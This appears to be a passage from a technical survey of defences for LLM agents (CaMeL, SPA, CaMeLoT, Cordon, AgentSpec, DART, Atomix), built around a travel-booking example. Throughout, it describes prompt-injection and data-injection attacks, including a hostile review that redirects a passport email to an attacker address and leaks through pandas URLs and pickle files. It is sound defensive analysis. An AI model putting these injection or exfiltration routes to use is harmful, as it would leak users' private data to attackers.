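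This system, named TACIT, also shows that a restricted language doesn't have to be small, since it uses Scala, a large general-purpose language. TACIT relies on capabilities, which are values that grant a permission, such as access to one folder. Scala's type system records which capabilities each piece of code can use, and the compiler rejects code that uses an undeclared capability. A safe mode removes features that could hide a capability from the compiler, including unchecked type conversions and reflection, which lets a program inspect and use its own internals while it runs. The essential requirement seems to be that code cannot have effects outside its declared permissions. A small language makes that easier because it has fewer features to examine.

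### Calls whose order matters

At the end of the booking example, Quasar's core rules allowed the three reservations and the confirmation email to be dispatched at the same time. The email's arguments are the customer's address and a fixed sentence, neither of which depends on the airline's answer, so the email could go out before the airline rejects the reservation. Following the core rules literally would therefore make this failure worse than in ordinary Python, which would have stopped at the failed flight before reserving the car or sending anything.

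Confluence does not protect against this, because it assumes that an external call depends only on its arguments. The email also depends on the trip existing, which its arguments don't capture. Even `print` has this problem, since two printed lines can share no data and still make sense in only one order.

Mell, Jia and colleagues (2026), in *PopPy*, describe the compiler that Quasar adapts and a way of handling such hidden dependencies. Their compiler adds a *sequence variable* to each external call. Every call receives this variable from the call before it and passes a new version to the next one:

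```
S1, r1 = reserve_hotel(S0, hotel)
S2, r2 = reserve_flight(S1, flight)
S3, r3 = reserve_car(S2, car)
S4, r4 = send_email(S3, customer, "Your trip is booked")
```

The email now needs `S3`, which comes from the car reservation, so the order of the original program has become a dependency between arguments. Applied strictly, this would also force the three searches to run one at a time. Developers therefore label each tool with an annotation that relaxes the order where it is safe to do so:

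- A `@sequential` call waits for all earlier sequential and read-only calls.
- A `@readonly` call waits only for earlier sequential calls.
- An `@unordered` call waits for neither and can start as soon as its arguments are ready.

PopPy treats a tool with no annotation as sequential, which is the cautious choice. For the booking agent, a developer could label the searches `@readonly` and leave the other tools unannotated. The searches would run at the same time, the reservations would follow in the order the model wrote them, and the email would go last.

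The formal guarantee is that a program makes the same external calls under PopPy as under standard Python, apart from reorderings that the annotations allow. If A is the set of annotations, and two sequences of calls are equivalent under ≡_A when permitted reorderings can turn one into the other, then for every program P:

calls(P under PopPy with A) ≡_A calls(P under Python)

The guarantee depends on A being correct. If a developer wrongly labels `send_email` as `@unordered`, the program can send the confirmation first without violating the theorem. The annotations also apply only within one program, so they would not stop the second agent from changing the hotel dates halfway through.

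Errors need separate treatment. Generated code in PopPy cannot catch an exception, the signal that Python raises when something fails. If any call might suddenly send the program somewhere else, the system cannot safely work ahead past it. PopPy therefore ends the program and reports the error, which leaves the customer with a hotel and no flight. A program can handle the failure only if the tool returns it as an ordinary value:

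```
reserve_hotel(hotel)
result = reserve_flight(flight)
if result == "sold out":
    cancel_hotel(hotel)
else:
    reserve_car(car)
    send_email(customer, "Your trip is booked")
```

This version also makes the car reservation and the email wait for the airline's response, even under Quasar's core rules, because both are now inside a branch that cannot begin until the response arrives. This depends on the model writing the check.

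### Powerful tools and faulty interpreters

All of these designs rely on the tools themselves being limited. Suppose a developer adds a tool called `run_shell`, which runs text as a shell command. The language still has no file or network operations, but a program can now call `run_shell` to read any file the tool can read and send it anywhere the tool can connect. A checker can detect the call, but the call reveals almost nothing about what the program will do.

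Odersky and colleagues acknowledge this limit in TACIT. Once an agent starts an external command, the type system's guarantee is only as strong as the list of permitted commands. They recommend allowing only specific safe commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`, and adding a sandbox where security is critical. But `sbt` is a build tool that runs code from a project's build files, so an agent that can edit those files can make `sbt` run a program of its choice.

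Libraries can reintroduce the same problem less visibly. Quasar can use any Python library by treating its functions as external calls, which keeps one of Python's main attractions. But `read_csv`, a function in the popular data-table library `pandas`, accepts a web address or a file name. A program that appears to load a table could therefore send a passport number to an attacker's server by including it in the address. The library's `read_pickle` function can run code hidden in the file it opens. A developer who makes all of `pandas` available adds hundreds of tools, probably without reviewing most of them.

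The interpreter is another point of failure, because a flaw in it could let a program do things the language is meant to prevent. Monty runs inside the developer's process to save time, so a serious flaw could expose that process's memory and credentials. TACIT depends on the correctness of the Scala compiler, the runtime and its own library of capabilities, and safe mode accepts some library code only because a programmer has marked it as safe. Running the interpreter in a container would limit the damage from such a flaw, but Monty would lose some of the speed that makes it attractive.

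A container can restrict a Python program to a finite list of effects just as well as a restricted language can, if the container's only link to the outside is a channel for tool calls. But a restricted language also makes it easier to examine or rearrange the program around those calls, as Quasar does when it collects several pending calls before running any of them. It can also start faster than a container and reject some faulty programs before they have done anything.

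None of this prevents the passport leak if the list contains a general `send_email` tool. A checker could reject the attacker's email only if it had information showing that the address came from a hotel review and that the attachment was the customer's private data.

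## Restricted programs that track where their data came from

An interpreter can track where data came from by attaching a label to every value. The label on an email address might show that it came from a hotel review, and the label on a passport number might show that only the customer and the airline may see it. When a program combines two values, the result inherits the restrictions on both. Security researchers call this method information-flow control and have studied it since the 1970s.

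A label can record a value's secrecy (who may see it) and its trustworthiness (whether an attacker could have chosen it). The two are independent. The user's passport number is secret and trustworthy, a public review is neither, and a private message from a stranger is secret but untrustworthy.

### How CaMeL works

The best-known agent design that uses such labels is Google DeepMind's CaMeL, which Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues described in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). It builds on an idea from Willison's *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023). A privileged model decides which tools to call but never reads untrusted text, and a quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools. Both can be copies of the same LLM, as they were when *ToolFence* (2026) tested CaMeL, because the protection comes from what each copy receives.

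Splitting the work this way stops an attacker from choosing the agent's actions. But as Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) explain in *CaMeLoT*, an extension of CaMeL, an attacker may still be able to change the data that goes into a correctly chosen tool call. CaMeL adds labels to deal with this. It handles a request as follows:

1. The privileged model receives the user's request and descriptions of the tools. It writes a program in a subset of Python that leaves out features such as arbitrary `while` loops.
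2. CaMeL's own interpreter runs the program. The results of tool calls go into variables, and the privileged model does not see what they contain.
3. If the program needs a fact from free text, it calls the quarantined model as if it were an ordinary function. The answer has to fit a fixed type, such as an email address.
4. The interpreter labels each value with its *Sources*, which record where it came from, and its *Readers*, which record who may see it.
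5. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that examines the tool, its arguments and their labels. The policy allows the call or denies it with a reason.

For example, one of CaMeL's policies for a banking agent lets the agent change a password only if the new password came from a trusted source. The CaMeL paper calls the labels capabilities, but unlike TACIT's capabilities, they describe data and do not grant permissions.

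### A hostile review in the booking program

Suppose the hotel search returns the review with the injected request for the customer's passport details. The privileged model wrote the booking program before the search ran, so the program sends only one email, to the customer. The review is stored in a variable. Even if the quarantined model later reads it and follows the injected instruction, that model can only return a value. It cannot add a second email to the program, so the attack fails without a policy check.

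The attacker has a better chance if the customer's own request involves a similar email. Suppose the hotel wants passport details in advance, and the customer asks the agent to find the front desk's address on the hotel's page and send them there. The privileged model might write:

```
hotel = cheapest(search_hotels("Lisbon", "3-6 June"))
page  = get_hotel_page(hotel)
desk  = query_ai_assistant(f"Find the front desk's email: {page}", EmailAddress)
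reserve_hotel(hotel)
send_email(desk, passport)
```

The page includes guest reviews, and one of them claims that the front desk has moved to `desk@visa-check.example`. The quarantined model believes it and returns that address, which is a perfectly valid email address. The program now has the right steps in the right order with the wrong recipient. At the last line, the interpreter has these labels:

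| Value | Sources | Readers |
|---|---|---|
| `page` | hotel's page | anyone |
| `desk` | hotel's page, quarantined model | anyone |
| `passport` | customer's files | customer, airline |

A sensible policy for `send_email` allows an email only if the recipient is among the Readers of everything in the message. The attacker's address isn't, so the interpreter denies the call.

The same policy would deny an email to the real front desk, unless somebody had added the front desk's address to the Readers. The labels record that the address came from a page that strangers can edit, but not whether it is correct. According to TechSpot, CaMeL can ask the user to confirm in such cases. The denial comes after `reserve_hotel` has run, so the reservation remains in place until the customer cancels it.

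A program can also leak information through a decision. If it sends an email only when the customer's bank balance exceeds a certain amount, the email reveals that the balance is above that amount, even though the message doesn't mention it. Researchers call this an implicit flow. CaMeL has a strict setting in which everything inside an `if` statement inherits the labels of the condition.

### CaMeL's results on AgentDojo

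When CaMeL appeared, Willison (2025) wrote in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* that it "finally bucks that trend" of little progress against prompt injection. Results on the AgentDojo benchmark support his view. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) reports that CaMeL eliminates nearly all of the benchmark's attacks, and *Kairos* (2026) found an attack success rate of about 0.4% when it reran CaMeL with its policies switched on.

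*AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports that the successful attacks in CaMeL's original evaluation were of two kinds. In the first, the user asked the agent to make a payment described in a document that the attacker controlled. CaMeL's developers place this outside their threat model, the list of attacks they set out to prevent. In the second, the agent quoted hotel reviews containing the attacker's text, which the AgentDojo benchmark counted as a successful attack. CaMeL also relies on the user's request being honest and on certain tools returning trustworthy data.

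Garby and colleagues reran CaMeL on AgentDojo's banking tasks with two newer models, GPT-5.2 and MiMo-v2.5. Attacks succeeded in 5 of the 622 attack runs that finished with the policies off, and in none of the 588 that finished with them on. Turning the policies on also roughly halved the number of legitimate tasks that CaMeL completed.

The policies had so little left to block because many of AgentDojo's attacks need a tool call or file access that a program written for the user's task would never contain. This is true of 97 of the 144 pairings of a banking task with an attack. Separating the two models is generally enough to defeat these attacks, so a near-perfect score on AgentDojo is good evidence that the separation works but much weaker evidence that the labels do.

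*Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (2026) tests the labels more directly. Its attacks plant false data, such as the wrong front-desk address, instead of instructions. CaMeL's strict setting stopped all of them. Every other defence in the comparison, including CaMeL's normal setting and CaMeL without policies, let through between 22.2% and 50.0% of them. The researchers also found an implementation fault that removed the untrusted label from data when the quarantined model extracted it. The method can evidently stop false data from reaching a sensitive tool, but only if the labels stay attached to the data at every step and the policies are precise.

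### SPA checks the whole plan first

CaMeL checks its policies one call at a time, which is why the hotel reservation went through before the email failed. Checking earlier is harder because CaMeL uses Python. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) notes that even the restricted subset keeps Python's dynamic typing, exceptions that can redirect a program, and the ability of programs to inspect themselves. It recommends replacing the subset with a language designed for security.

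The JSON plans in *SPA* are close to this recommendation. The planning model writes one complete plan per user request, using six kinds of step:

- `tool` calls an outside tool and is the only step that can have an external effect.
- `q-llm` asks a quarantined model to turn text into structured data.
- `retrieve` loads a result saved from an earlier request.
- `condition` chooses between two branches.
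- `loop` repeats some steps for each item in a list.
- `display` shows something to the user.

The language has no arithmetic, user-defined functions, or templates that insert values into text. A condition can make only one comparison, so a plan has to express "cheap and near the beach" as one condition inside another. Loops can only go through a list. Each variable is assigned once, and a variable created inside a branch or loop disappears when that branch or loop ends. These restrictions let the checker determine exactly which earlier values each step depends on by reading the plan.

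Each value has a label (C, I), where C is its level of secrecy and I its level of trustworthiness, which security researchers call integrity. In the simplest version, public is below private and untrusted is below trusted. When a step combines two values, SPA keeps the higher secrecy and the lower trustworthiness:

(c₁, i₁) ⊔ (c₂, i₂) = (max(c₁, c₂), min(i₁, i₂))

Each tool has a policy that gives the highest secrecy it may receive, C_in, and the lowest trustworthiness it will accept, I_in. Data with the label (C, I) may enter the tool only if

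C ≤ C_in and I ≥ I_in

In the front-desk example, the hotel's page is labeled (public, untrusted). The quarantined model's output inherits the labels of its input, so the address is also (public, untrusted). The passport is (private, trusted), so the arguments of `send_email` have the combined label (private, untrusted). If the policy for `send_email` is (public, trusted), the call fails both tests and SPA rejects the plan before it reserves the hotel.

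SPA also applies labels to decisions, which makes it very strict. In the original booking program, the confirmation email goes out only if the total price is within the budget. The prices come from outside websites, so SPA treats the condition and every step inside it as untrusted. Under the policy above, it would reject even a fixed message to the customer, because anyone who controls a price could determine whether the message goes out. To allow the email, the person deploying the agent would have to trust the price data or relax the email policy. SPA sets one requirement for all of a tool's arguments, whereas CaMeL's policies can treat the recipient and the message differently. SPA's rule is easier to analyse but handles ordinary cases like the confirmation email less well.

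If the checker rejects a plan, SPA ends the request without giving the planning model a reason. Girrens and Wang designed it this way to prevent a model from revising an unsafe plan until it passes. If text intended for the user contains a forbidden item, SPA instead replaces that item with a redaction marker and displays the rest.

Labels also stay with saved results. A customer might ask the agent on Monday to save a hotel's details and on Tuesday to book "the hotel we discussed". The planning model then sees a description of the saved result but not its contents, so an instruction hidden in the hotel's listing cannot influence the new plan. If the plan retrieves the details, they still carry the label they had on Monday.

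Girrens and Wang tested SPA with GPT-5.4-nano on 949 AgentDojo attack runs. Four attacks succeeded without the labels and none with them, partly because SPA rejected many plans, including legitimate ones. In a version that spread each task over several requests, AgentDojo counted 0.2% of attacks as successful with the labels, including two runs in which SPA had already rejected the plan. Girrens and Wang acknowledge that these attacks are a weak test of saved data because they were not designed to lie dormant until a later request.

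### CaMeLoT adds rules about order

A policy that checks one call at a time can't easily express a rule about the whole program. For example, it can check that a confirmation email goes to the customer, but it can't easily require the agent to reserve the flight before confirming the trip. Nikolaou and colleagues designed CaMeLoT to check such rules before CaMeL runs a program.

CaMeLoT converts the privileged model's program into a finite-state machine, which represents the points the program can reach and the possible moves between them. It labels each point with the tool being called, the tools already called, and whether any argument came from an untrusted source. A model checker then examines every possible path through the machine. CaMeLoT does not determine which branch a condition will take or how many times a loop will repeat, so it includes every possibility.

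The rules use temporal logic, a notation for statements about what happens over time. In words, one rule for the booking agent could be: *the program must never send the email unless it has already called the flight-reservation tool*. In notation, it is

**AG**(call_send_email ⇒ reserve_flight_called)

**A** means "on every route" and **G** means "at every point". The arrow means "only if", so the program may call `send_email` only if an earlier step called `reserve_flight`. The rule does not require the program to book anything, so the booking program can still stop without making a reservation if the trip is too expensive. Other operators can require something to happen eventually, such as the agent closing every support ticket it opens.

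If a program breaks a rule, the model checker finds a path that leads to the violation. CaMeLoT describes this path to the privileged model, which tries to repair the program. Girrens and Wang deliberately ruled out this kind of feedback in SPA. The feedback seems less dangerous in CaMeLoT, because it comes from the program's structure and no tool has yet returned text that an attacker could have written. It still gives a misguided model several attempts to find a program that satisfies the rules without doing what the rules' authors intended.

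Nikolaou and colleagues wrote seven ordering and safety rules for an agent that handles computer-security alerts, along with seven programs that each broke one rule. CaMeLoT caught all seven programs, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught one. They chose rules that CaMeL was not built to express, so the result shows what CaMeLoT's notation can express, not how often real agents make such mistakes. CaMeLoT could also reproduce 22 of CaMeL's 28 policies for AgentDojo's tools as checks made before execution. Most of the others depend on facts available only at run time, such as who currently has access to a file, so CaMeL still has to check them as the program runs.

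CaMeLoT records that the program called `reserve_flight`, but not whether the airline accepted the reservation. If the tool returns "sold out" as an ordinary value and the program ignores it, the program still sends the confirmation email without violating the rule.

### What the labels do not guarantee

All these systems depend on people writing the right policies. A developer might label hotel listings as trusted because they come from a reputable booking site, forgetting that the hotels write them. Every later check would then use the wrong label, even if the check itself worked correctly. A policy can also be too narrow. FIDES, the labelling system in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025), let an attacker put an unrequested event on a user's calendar because the event had no other participants and so leaked nothing.

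Even with good policies, the interpreter may lose track of information. Garby and colleagues found that CaMeL can miss information revealed when a program skips a step. They also found that CaMeL doesn't track labels in the loop that asks the privileged model to try again after a program fails. Each failure can therefore reveal a little about secret data, and repeated failures can reveal much more.

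Garby and colleagues' alternative is the LLMbda calculus, a small language whose interpreter has a machine-checked proof of noninterference: changing secret inputs cannot change any public output, and changing untrusted inputs cannot change any trusted output. The proof covers programs that a model writes and runs during execution, but not what somebody might learn from whether a program finishes. It holds only if developers have labelled the data sources correctly and put checks on all the sensitive tools. The agent practises on simulated tools first, which avoids CaMeL's retry problem and prevents failed attempts from repeating real effects.

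Labels can also disappear when one agent passes work to another. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, connected three agents that each ran CaMeL without policies. One agent read job applications from a database, a second coordinated the work, and a third sent messages. The coordinator included a summary of the applications in its request to the messaging agent, which treated the whole request as a trusted instruction from its user. An injection in the database could therefore make the messaging agent send the applicants' data to an outsider, even though every agent followed CaMeL's rules.

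Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed this by sending instructions and untrusted data through separate channels. In their multi-agent version of AgentDojo, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent ran CaMeL separately, and 0.0% with the separate channels. The weakness exists, but the benchmark's attacks rarely exploited it.

A harder case is a request to follow a document, such as "Book whatever my assistant's itinerary says." The request is genuine, but it gives control of the booking to anyone who can edit the itinerary. In the LLMbda calculus, a program can handle such requests by *endorsing* a value, explicitly relabelling it as trusted. Agents using this feature resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attack runs on AgentDojo's banking tasks. In both failures, the user had asked the agent to make a payment described in a file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents.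 Removing endorsement blocks this attack but also prevents the agent from making the payment when the file is genuine.

A broad request can undo the separation between the two models. One banking task asks the agent to follow a file's instructions precisely. In two runs of CaMeL without policies, the privileged model wrote a program that could call any tool the file named, so the file's author could choose the agent's actions. SPA's four failures when run without labels came from the same task.

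Correctly labelled text can still be false. Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on AgentDojo and recorded only one successful attack. The user had asked the agent to book a particular hotel, and the attacker had planted a recommendation for a different one in that hotel's reviews. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, and AgentDojo scored the mention of the other hotel as a successful attack. Odersky and colleagues reasonably blame the benchmark's scoring, since their policy allows the agent to show public reviews to the user. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* reports similar cases and suggests marking such text as untrustworthy when the agent displays it.

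A mark like this could help a customer who reads the reviews before choosing a hotel, but it helps less when the agent makes the choice. The agent has to choose from listings that the hotels wrote, so a policy that barred untrusted data from `reserve_hotel` would block every booking. If the policy allows that data, a false claim in a listing can determine which hotel the agent reserves, even when every label is correct.

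## The case for holding effects back until the whole task is checked

CaMeL checks each tool call as it comes up, while SPA and CaMeLoT check a whole plan in advance. Supporters of transactions want to check later. The agent works with real search results and command output while the runtime holds back the agent's effects. When the task is complete, the runtime examines everything together and either releases or discards the effects.

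The reason to wait is that each call in a task can be acceptable when the sequence is not. Reserving a hotel is sensible, and it becomes a mistake only if the flight falls through. The main example in Chen and colleagues' paper on Cordon, their transactional runtime, concerns a leak. A company asks an agent to diagnose an outage, and the agent does four things:

1. It reads the application logs, which happen to contain an API key, a password that programs use.
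2. It runs commands that summarise the failures.
3. It writes a note on how to fix the problem.
4. It prepares a Slack message for the engineers on call.

The agent has to read the logs to make a diagnosis, and the engineers expect a message. But the message draws on a summary of a log that contains a key, and everyone in the Slack channel can read the message.

Chen and colleagues turn this into a general argument. Let H be the full history of a run, and let π_M(H) be the part of it that a safety mechanism M can observe. If H ends in a forbidden effect, another history H′ ends in a legitimate one, and π_M(H) = π_M(H′), then M cannot reliably block the first and allow the second. For example, the Slack message might say that the failures began with `7f3a91c2`. The message is useful if that string identifies a software release, but it is a leak if the string is the API key. A filter that reads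 only the message cannot distinguish the two cases because the text is identical.

The argument is sound, but a checker can use the history of a task without waiting for the task to end. An interpreter like CaMeL's would label the log as secret, carry the label over to the summary and refuse the Slack call at step 4. The leak is therefore mainly a reason to track data, rather than to hold effects back. Waiting helps when a later event turns an earlier call into a mistake. For example, no label on the hotel reservation could have shown that the airline was about to run out of seats. Waiting also helps with cleanup. If a per-call check blocks the Slack message, the note from step 3 is already on disk and may also contain the key, whereas a transaction can discard both the note and the message.

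### Rules for individual calls

Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AGENTSPEC*, created a small language for rules that run before an agent acts. Each rule names a triggering event, some conditions and a response. A rule for the agent investigating the outage might be:

```
rule @inspect_slack
trigger send_slack
check contains_api_key
enforce user_inspection
end
```

One AgentSpec rule runs `contains_api_key`, a function the developer supplies, before the agent sends a Slack message. If the function returns true, AgentSpec asks the user whether to send the message. Rules can also stop the agent, carry out a fixed action or make the model reconsider. Evaluating the conditions takes only a few milliseconds.

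This works well when the last call reveals the danger. In tests with a simulated household robot, the agent carried out up to 79% of the hazardous instructions in one category without AgentSpec, and none in any category with it. Its success rate on safe tasks fell from 58.6% to 54.3%. Some hazards took several steps. In one, the robot fills a mug with water, picks it up, finds a laptop and pours the water on it. Filling a mug is harmless, so the rule applies only to `pour` and checks what the water would land on.

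AgentSpec is weaker when the danger depends on how data moved between steps. One of its rules asks the user to inspect any program that both fetches an untrusted web page and prints something. The rule does not check whether the program prints what it fetched. Wang and colleagues acknowledge that analysing the flow of data would make the rule more accurate. AgentSpec can also run rules when the agent finishes its task, but it does not hold effects back, so the agent has already sent the Slack message by then.

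All three of AgentSpec's developers later worked on *Representation Transitions Reveal Emerging Safety Risks in Multi-Turn LLM Agents* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), which describes this limit. The paper used a benchmark that splits each harmful task into a series of individually permissible requests. AgentSpec's rules did not fire on these attacks because every call satisfied them.

The paper proposes DART, which monitors the model's internal activations for signs of a developing attack. DART flagged every attack in the benchmark and raised false alarms in an average of 12% of harmless conversations. Yet the attack success rate, measured by whether the model's final response was a refusal, fell only from 84% to 25%. When DART detects an attack, it adds a warning to the model's input, and some models continued despite the warning. Detecting an attack is evidently not enough if the model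 still decides whether to stop.

A compromise is to check each call during the task in light of the earlier ones. *AgentTrust* (2026) reports that most production guardrails check each call separately, and that earlier research offers no detector that fires when part of a sequence matches a known dangerous chain. Such a detector could flag an agent that has read and encoded a secret and is about to upload it, without having to delay harmless calls. But it would catch only the chains that somebody had listed, and it could not undo calls that had already run.

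### How Cordon runs a task

Cordon sits between an agent and its tools. The model still makes ordinary tool calls, but Cordon assigns all the calls in a task to one transaction, even when they are spread over several turns. It then handles them as follows:

1. **Registration.** Cordon records the tool, its arguments and the task. If a tool cannot describe what it reads or changes, Cordon rejects the call or records that it falls outside the transaction's protection.
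2. **Private copies of files.** The agent's changes to files go into a *shadow state*. Later steps in the same task read from it, so the agent can reopen a note it has just written while everyone else still has the old files. To run a command, Cordon copies the working folder, adds the pending changes and runs the command there in a sandbox, by default without network access. Afterwards it looks for files that the command created, changed or deleted.
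3. **An outbox for external actions.** Messages and other outward-facing actions wait in an *effect outbox*. Each entry contains the destination, the content, a record of where the content came from, the agent's authority to send it and an identifier that helps prevent duplicates.
4. **A graph of results.** Cordon gives each result an identifier and adds an arrow whenever one result contributes to another, or to a file or message. The outage example produces the path log → summary → Slack message.
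5. **Validation.** Cordon checks the graph, the changed files, the outbox and the agent's permissions together.
6. **Commit or abort.** If the transaction passes, Cordon moves the changed files into the real workspace and releases the messages. Otherwise it discards the private copies and cancels the messages, and in tests this rollback took a median of about 4 milliseconds.

Chen and colleagues state the condition for a commit as

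commit(T) ⇒ valid(T, Cₜ) ∧ staged(E) ∧ recoverable(W, D)

T is the transaction, E its external effects, W its file writes and D its deletions, and ∧ means "and". Cₜ is the constraints at time t, which consist of the user's current intent, the agent's authority and the system's policy. Cordon may commit only if the transaction is valid, its external effects are still waiting in the outbox, and Cordon can still restore the files. Because Cordon uses the constraints in force at validation, a user who withdraws permission halfway through a task can still stop the message from going out.

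Nine rules define a valid transaction. One forbids any path in the graph from a secret to an unauthorised destination. Another forbids using untrusted input to justify a change to a sensitive file unless the constraints allow it. In the outage example, the decision depends on whether the Slack channel is authorised to receive material derived from the log. If it isn't, the first of these two rules blocks even a harmless message that the checkout service failed at 14:05, because that fact came from the same log.

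The graph is probably the hardest part to get right. CaMeL's interpreter computes every value in a program, so it can follow data from one variable to the next. In Cordon, the model may read the log and write the summary in its own words, and the runtime cannot easily determine which parts of the log influenced a sentence. If it records only the connections it detects, it may miss a leak. If it assumes that everything the model writes depends on everything the model has read, reading a single secret restricts the rest of the task. Chen and colleagues treat the graph as evidence for the decision to commit, and do not claim to prove that secrets cannot influence public output.

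Cordon also covers only operations that pass through it. A plugin with hidden side effects could send the key somewhere without leaving anything in the outbox to cancel.

### The test on 45 risky workflows

To test containment, Chen and colleagues wrote 45 workflows in areas such as coding, customer support and office work. They combined nine kinds of existing defence with five kinds of risk:

- direct writes to sensitive files
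- sensitive writes hidden inside a command
- external actions that reveal a secret from the session
- commands that send out data derived from a secret
- deletions that affect a large number of files

For each kind of defence, the evaluation of Cordon used an adapter, a simplified version that had only the information such a defence normally receives. Every workflow ran with no defence, with the relevant adapter and with Cordon.

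| | Stopped before commit | Detected only afterwards | Missed |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 0 | 0 | 45 |
| Adapters | 14 | 5 | 26 |
| Cordon | 45 | 0 | 0 |

In one workflow, an agent investigating a checkout problem reads a setup note and runs a helper command that looks routine. The command adds data to a configuration file for SSH, a system for logging in to other computers. This change is not visible in the tool request, but Cordon finds it in its private copy and blocks it. In another workflow, a cleanup command deletes far too many files inside a folder the agent is allowed to use. A sandbox permits each deletion because the file is in that folder, but Cordon counts the pending deletions and aborts when they exceed a limit.

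These examples support the case for waiting better than the Slack leak does. It is hard to tell from reading an unfamiliar command what it will change, and much easier to run it on a copy and look. The workflows that an adapter detected too late also support waiting. Monitors that read the record of a finished run recognised the risky behaviour, but the effects had already happened.

The score of 45 out of 45 mainly shows that the prototype works as intended on the problems its designers had in mind. Chen and colleagues built both the workflows and the adapters, and they chose risks that become visible at the level of a transaction. Cordon's own validity rules also define what counts as a violation in such tests, so a system that enforces those rules correctly should do very well.

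The adapters' total of 14 pools nine kinds of defence, each tested on five workflows. It does not measure how well any single defence works, or what a company would stop by using several together, such as a sandbox, an output filter and permission prompts. All the runs used one model, DeepSeek-V4-Pro, and none involved an attacker who knew how Cordon worked and tried to get around it.

Every workflow in the set contained a risk, so the test does not measure how often Cordon would block a legitimate task of the same kind, such as a cleanup that should delete hundreds of files. Chen and colleagues did run ordinary tasks from other benchmarks, and Cordon made little difference to the scores.

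A final check also needs a rule for each problem it is meant to catch. Without a rule that covers the planted hotel listing, Cordon could hold back every effect of a booking at that hotel and still detect no violation.

### Discarding failed work

Sun and colleagues have a different reason for using transactions in their ACID-Agent, which answers questions by analysing collections of data files. They want to prevent a mistake in one step from spoiling later steps.

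An agentic transaction is a sequence of steps τ = ⟨r₁, …, rₙ⟩, where each step rᵢ = (cᵢ, aᵢ, fᵢ) contains the model's context, the action it takes and the feedback it receives. ACID-Agent divides this sequence into smaller cycles that each act as a transaction. In each cycle, the agent explores the data with read-only code, writes and runs code for the next part of the analysis, and then validates the result. If validation succeeds, the agent commits the new files and its memory of the attempt. If validation fails, it discards both and tries again with feedback on what went wrong. It can retry each cycle up to twice.

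Validation looks for error messages, asks a language model to review the work, and tests whether the code relies on what the agent found during exploration. For this last test, a small model estimates how probable each token of the code is. ACID-Agent combines these probabilities into a confidence score:

confidence = exp((1/n) × Σ log pᵢ)

Here n is the number of tokens and pᵢ is the probability of token i. Two tokens with probabilities of 0.9 and 0.4 give a score of 0.6. ACID-Agent calculates the score once with the exploration notes and once without them. Suppose the code selects records from 2019. If the small model assigns that choice about the same probability both times, the notes probably did not support it, and the agent tries again.

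Sun and colleagues report that ACID-Agent outperformed leading agents, including Claude Code, by 10.6 percentage points on KramaBench, a set of 104 data-analysis tasks. With the model Qwen3.5-397B, Claude Code scored 64.0% and ACID-Agent 74.6%. With the stronger GLM-5.2, the gap shrank to 3.2 points (74.2% against 77.4%), while the average cost of a task rose from $0.12 to $0.61.

KramaBench measures how well an agent analyses data, not whether it leaks secrets, sends unwanted messages or leaves bookings half finished. The validation step would not necessarily help with those problems either, because it favours code based on evidence from the files, and a false record planted by an attacker would also look like evidence.

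A version of ACID-Agent that kept its failed attempts in its workspace and memory scored 78.3%, compared with 90.0% for the full system. This suggests that undoing failed work can make an agent more accurate as well as safer to run. But the comparison used only one of the benchmark's six subject areas, the one where ACID-Agent had gained the most over Claude Code with the same model. The failed attempts also consisted of files and notes that the agent controlled, and discarding those is much easier than cancelling a hotel reservation.

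### When a placeholder is not enough

Holding a call back has an awkward consequence. The tool has not run, so the runtime has no real result to give the agent. Atomix, the runtime that Mohammadi and colleagues built, instead returns an acknowledgement that it has staged or queued the call. This is fine for a confirmation email at the end of a task, since the agent does not need anything back. It is less useful for a reservation:

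```
booking = reserve_hotel(hotel)
order_airport_transfer(booking.reference)
if booking.cancellation_fee > 100:
    buy_insurance(booking)
```

If the runtime holds back `reserve_hotel`, the booking has no reference yet. The runtime could perhaps hold back the airport transfer too and fill in the reference when it commits both. That does not work for the third line, because the program needs the fee before it can choose whether to buy insurance. In the ordinary agent loop, a model that needs a reference might also treat the acknowledgement as one or make one up.

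A held-back call also cannot fail until it runs. If the runtime holds all three reservations and the email until the end, the transaction could pass every check even though the flight has sold out. The flight reservation would fail only when the runtime released the calls, possibly after the hotel had accepted its reservation, which would again leave the customer with a room and no flight.

Cordon avoids this problem for files because the agent can read and test its private copy, but the agent has no such copy of an external system like an airline's. Chen and colleagues include API calls among the effects held in the outbox, but do not specify what the agent receives while a call is waiting. In their outage example, the Slack message comes last, so no later step depends on it.

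Atomix offers a practical reply, which is to hold back only what has to wait. It divides effects into three main classes:

| Effect | When the tool runs | What the agent receives | If the transaction aborts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reversible, such as a cancellable reservation | Immediately | The real result | Atomix runs a compensation |
| Bufferable, such as a local file write | At commit | A "staged" acknowledgement | Atomix discards it |
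| Irreversible, such as an email | At commit | A "queued" acknowledgement | Atomix discards it |

In the booking example, Atomix makes the reservations immediately and gives the agent the providers' real confirmations, but it holds back the email. If the airline has no seats, the agent gets that result right away, and Atomix cancels the hotel and discards the email. Just before committing a transaction, Atomix can also run a check on everything the transaction has read and changed. Mohammadi and colleagues leave it to the developer to write this check.

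The drawback, as with a saga, is that outsiders can see the reservations before anyone has checked the whole task. This seems acceptable for ordinary booking failures, because the agent often can't finish the task without real answers.

Running reversible calls immediately works less well when the danger is a leak. Suppose the agent follows instructions in a hostile review and puts the customer's passport number in the "special requests" field of the hotel reservation. Atomix would make the reservation immediately because the hotel allows cancellations. Cancelling it later releases the room, but the hotel still has the passport number. Even a search can leak data, because the agent sends its search terms to an outside website, and a runtime can't hold back a search whose results the agent needs. Any call that runs immediately therefore needs its arguments checked before it runs, and labels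 like CaMeL's are well suited to this. Mohammadi and colleagues likewise describe Atomix as something to combine with information-flow control.

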